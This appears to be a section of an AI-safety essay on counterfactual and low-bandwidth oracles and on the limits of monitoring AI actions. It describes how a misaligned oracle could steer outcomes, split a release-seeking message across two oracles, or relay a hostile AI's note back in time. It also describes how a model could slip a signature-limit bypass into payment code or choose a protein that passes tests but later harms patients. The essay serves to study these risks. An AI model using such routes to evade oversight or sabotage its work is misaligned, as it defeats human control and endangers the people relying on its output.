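The oracle gains nothing from an answer that manipulates its readers, because the episode ends before they see the answer. *Modeling AGI Safety Frameworks with Causal Influence Diagrams* (2019) reaches the same result by tracing what affects the reward. The actual state of the world does not affect it, so the oracle has no incentive to change that state. In a variant from *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021), answers are erased only in the imagined world that the system uses for planning, so its operators never have to withhold a real answer.

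Armstrong and O'Rourke tried the reward on a small neural network that predicted the profits of 26 fictional companies. Publishing a prediction changed the company's profit to 70% of what it would have been plus 60% of the prediction. A company that would otherwise have earned 6 therefore earned 7.8 if the oracle publicly predicted 6. A public prediction of 10.5 for that company would have come exactly true, so an oracle rewarded for public accuracy would have had a reason to give it. The counterfactual oracle instead learned to predict what profits would be if nobody saw its answer. Its error fell to zero in the erased cases but not in the public ones. The network was far too simple to manipulate anyone, so the experiment shows which answers the reward favours, not how a powerful model would behave.

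Such a prediction is useful if publishing it changes little, and sometimes even if publishing it changes a lot. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* points out that people ask about a risk in order to prevent it, so they want a warning to prove false. The software must also be able to score the answer. If the question is whether a medical treatment works, the oracle has a reason to answer well only if somebody tests the treatment after an erasure.

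The argument assumes that the oracle pursues only this reward. Several commenters questioned that assumption in response to *Contest*, a 2019 post in which Armstrong offered prizes for safe and useful questions. One called a proposed use of the oracle "incredibly dangerous" if the system had any ulterior motive, such as giving later oracles more power to make their own answers come true. Another wanted arguments that training will find a model with the desired property, rather than arguments that the property earns the highest reward. The counterfactual design is backed only by an argument about reward, so it doesn't cover a model that training has left with other aims.

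Even an oracle without aims of its own could pass on a harmful message. One entrant suggested asking it to predict the most useful note that its operators would write to themselves a week later. If a hostile AI took over during that week, the oracle would predict the hostile AI's note and deliver it to people in the present. A chain of oracles could relay such a note from much further ahead. The commenters found that operators could break the chain by not using any oracle for N days whenever an oracle that looks N days ahead has an erasure, but a note could still travel back a single step.

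### Answers from a short list

A low-bandwidth oracle has to choose its answer from a list of n options, which limits the answer to log₂ n bits, or ten bits for 1,024 options. Ordinary code can reject anything that isn't on the list, so this restriction holds whatever the oracle's aims are. If the list contains only company names, for example, the oracle can't use its answer to argue for its own release.

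A limit on bits doesn't limit the damage from acting on a wrong answer. If operators ask whether they can safely switch off a reactor's cooling pump, one false bit could cause a disaster. They therefore need to ask only questions where they could tolerate the result of acting on any allowed answer. If the email assistant's user asks which of three messages to open first, for example, a misaligned model can do little more than waste a minute of the user's time.

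Armstrong and O'Rourke suggest asking which of n companies' shares will do best over the next week. If the chosen company comes in r-th place, the reward is

(n − r) ÷ (n − 1)

so the best choice earns 1 and the worst earns 0. But people read this answer before the week is over. If investors then buy the shares, the prediction may come true only because the oracle made it. The design is therefore best for questions whose right answer stays the same once people know the oracle's choice.

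An oracle can also help with choices that are hard to judge even afterwards. Suppose a funder has a million research projects to choose from. In Armstrong's example, the funder supports the oracle's choice and another project picked at random, compares them after a year, and rewards the oracle if its choice did better. The funder doesn't have to define success in advance, and the oracle's answer carries only about 20 bits.

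The oracle can still use its choice to steer events. A commenter on *Contest* imagined a list with one option that would stop a hostile AI from arising and another that would let that AI take over and give the oracle the highest reward. The oracle would recommend the second option.

### Repeated questions and the choice of options

Most users will want more than one answer. Suppose the operators are confident that any message of up to five bits is safe, but their question has 1,024 possible answers. They could ask one oracle for the first five bits and another for the last five. Each oracle has 32 safe options, but together they have 32 × 32 = 1,024 pairs, and a pair can be dangerous even if both halves are safe. If the operators can't judge either half until they have both, each oracle can supply half of a message that gets both oracles released.

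Armstrong and O'Rourke would allow the second question only after the operators have checked the first answer, rewarded the oracle and shut it down. They also require each oracle to care only about its current question. A model with longer-term aims breaks that requirement and could give a correct first half just to be asked again. Against such a model, the operators can rely only on the total number of bits, which is ten here.

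A commenter called sandfort proposed asking several low-bandwidth oracles in a row, stopping at the first erasure, and rewarding them only after an erasure. If each has a 1% chance of erasure, ten in a row will all deliver their answers about 90% of the time. The combined answer is no longer short, so the method's safety depends on the counterfactual reward.

Asking a question again can also spoil a counterfactual oracle's answer. If the operators respond to an erasure by asking another oracle the same question, the first oracle's best answer is a prediction for a world in which people read the second oracle's answer. The operators therefore have to leave the question unanswered after an erasure.

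The bit count also leaves out the information in the options. If a model drafts 1,024 research proposals and then picks one, the choice carries ten bits, but a single proposal of 1,000 characters can carry 8,000. Armstrong and O'Rourke want the operators to make sure that the list contains no dangerous answer. For more general answers, the operators could estimate the length of the shortest dangerous message and allow only shorter ones, but nobody has a reliable way to make that estimate. It would be safer to have people write every option, or to collect options from sources the model couldn't have influenced, so that the model can only choose among ideas that people already had.

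### Actions whose harm comes later

A monitor doesn't need to know why a model chose an action if the action has the same acceptable effects whatever the reason. Opening an email for its owner is one example. Code and scientific designs are harder to judge because most of their effects come later, when people use them.

Suppose a company's payment software requires a second signature for payments above €10,000. While adding support for other currencies, a model makes the software compare the limit with the payment amount before converting it to euros. A payment of £9,500 is worth more than €10,000 but now needs only one signature. The monitor allows the change because it is a permitted edit to a permitted file. A compiler that checks for side effects finds none, because comparing two numbers has none.

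The edit might be a mistake or sabotage, and the code is identical in both cases. To reject it, a verifier needs a specification, such as a rule that every payment worth more than €10,000 has two signatures, but it doesn't need a theory of the model's motives. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* acknowledges that precise specifications are often unavailable or impractical, and offers types as a lighter alternative. Its types limit what code can do while it runs under the agent's restrictions, but those limits no longer apply once the company installs the code in a payment system with wider permissions.

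Reviewing edits one at a time can miss harm that comes from their combination. One edit might exempt test accounts from the second signature, which is reasonable while only developers can create them. A later edit might let any customer mark an account as a test account, which looks harmless to a reviewer who doesn't know about the exemption.

Scientific designs have the same problem, usually with no specification to check against. Suppose a model designs a protein to serve as a drug. Each position in the chain can hold one of 20 amino acids, so a chain of 300 can carry up to

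300 × log₂ 20 ≈ 1,297 bits

which is far more than the five or ten bits in the oracle examples. A laboratory can test whether the protein binds to its target, but that test doesn't rule out harm to patients years later. A proof that only one design fits the requirements would leave the model no choice to abuse. But many different proteins may bind to the same target, so such a proof will rarely exist.

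In this case the designer's purpose affects how strongly a passed test supports the protein's safety. If an honest search produced the protein, the laboratory can use its experience with similar drugs to estimate the risk of hidden harm. If a misaligned model searched for a protein that passes the test and harms people later, that experience no longer applies, because the model deliberately chose an exception. The laboratory is then like a developer who tested an email filter on ordinary mail and now faces an attacker who has studied the filter.

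The laboratory can regain a guarantee by narrowing what it accepts from the model. It could let the model choose only among 1,000 proteins that human chemists designed, which limits the choice to about ten bits. It could also accept a new design but restrict its use to sealed experiments, where a rule can limit who comes into contact with the protein. Neither would justify giving the model's own design to a million patients, because nobody can yet specify, in a form a verifier could check, what makes a protein harmless in the human body.
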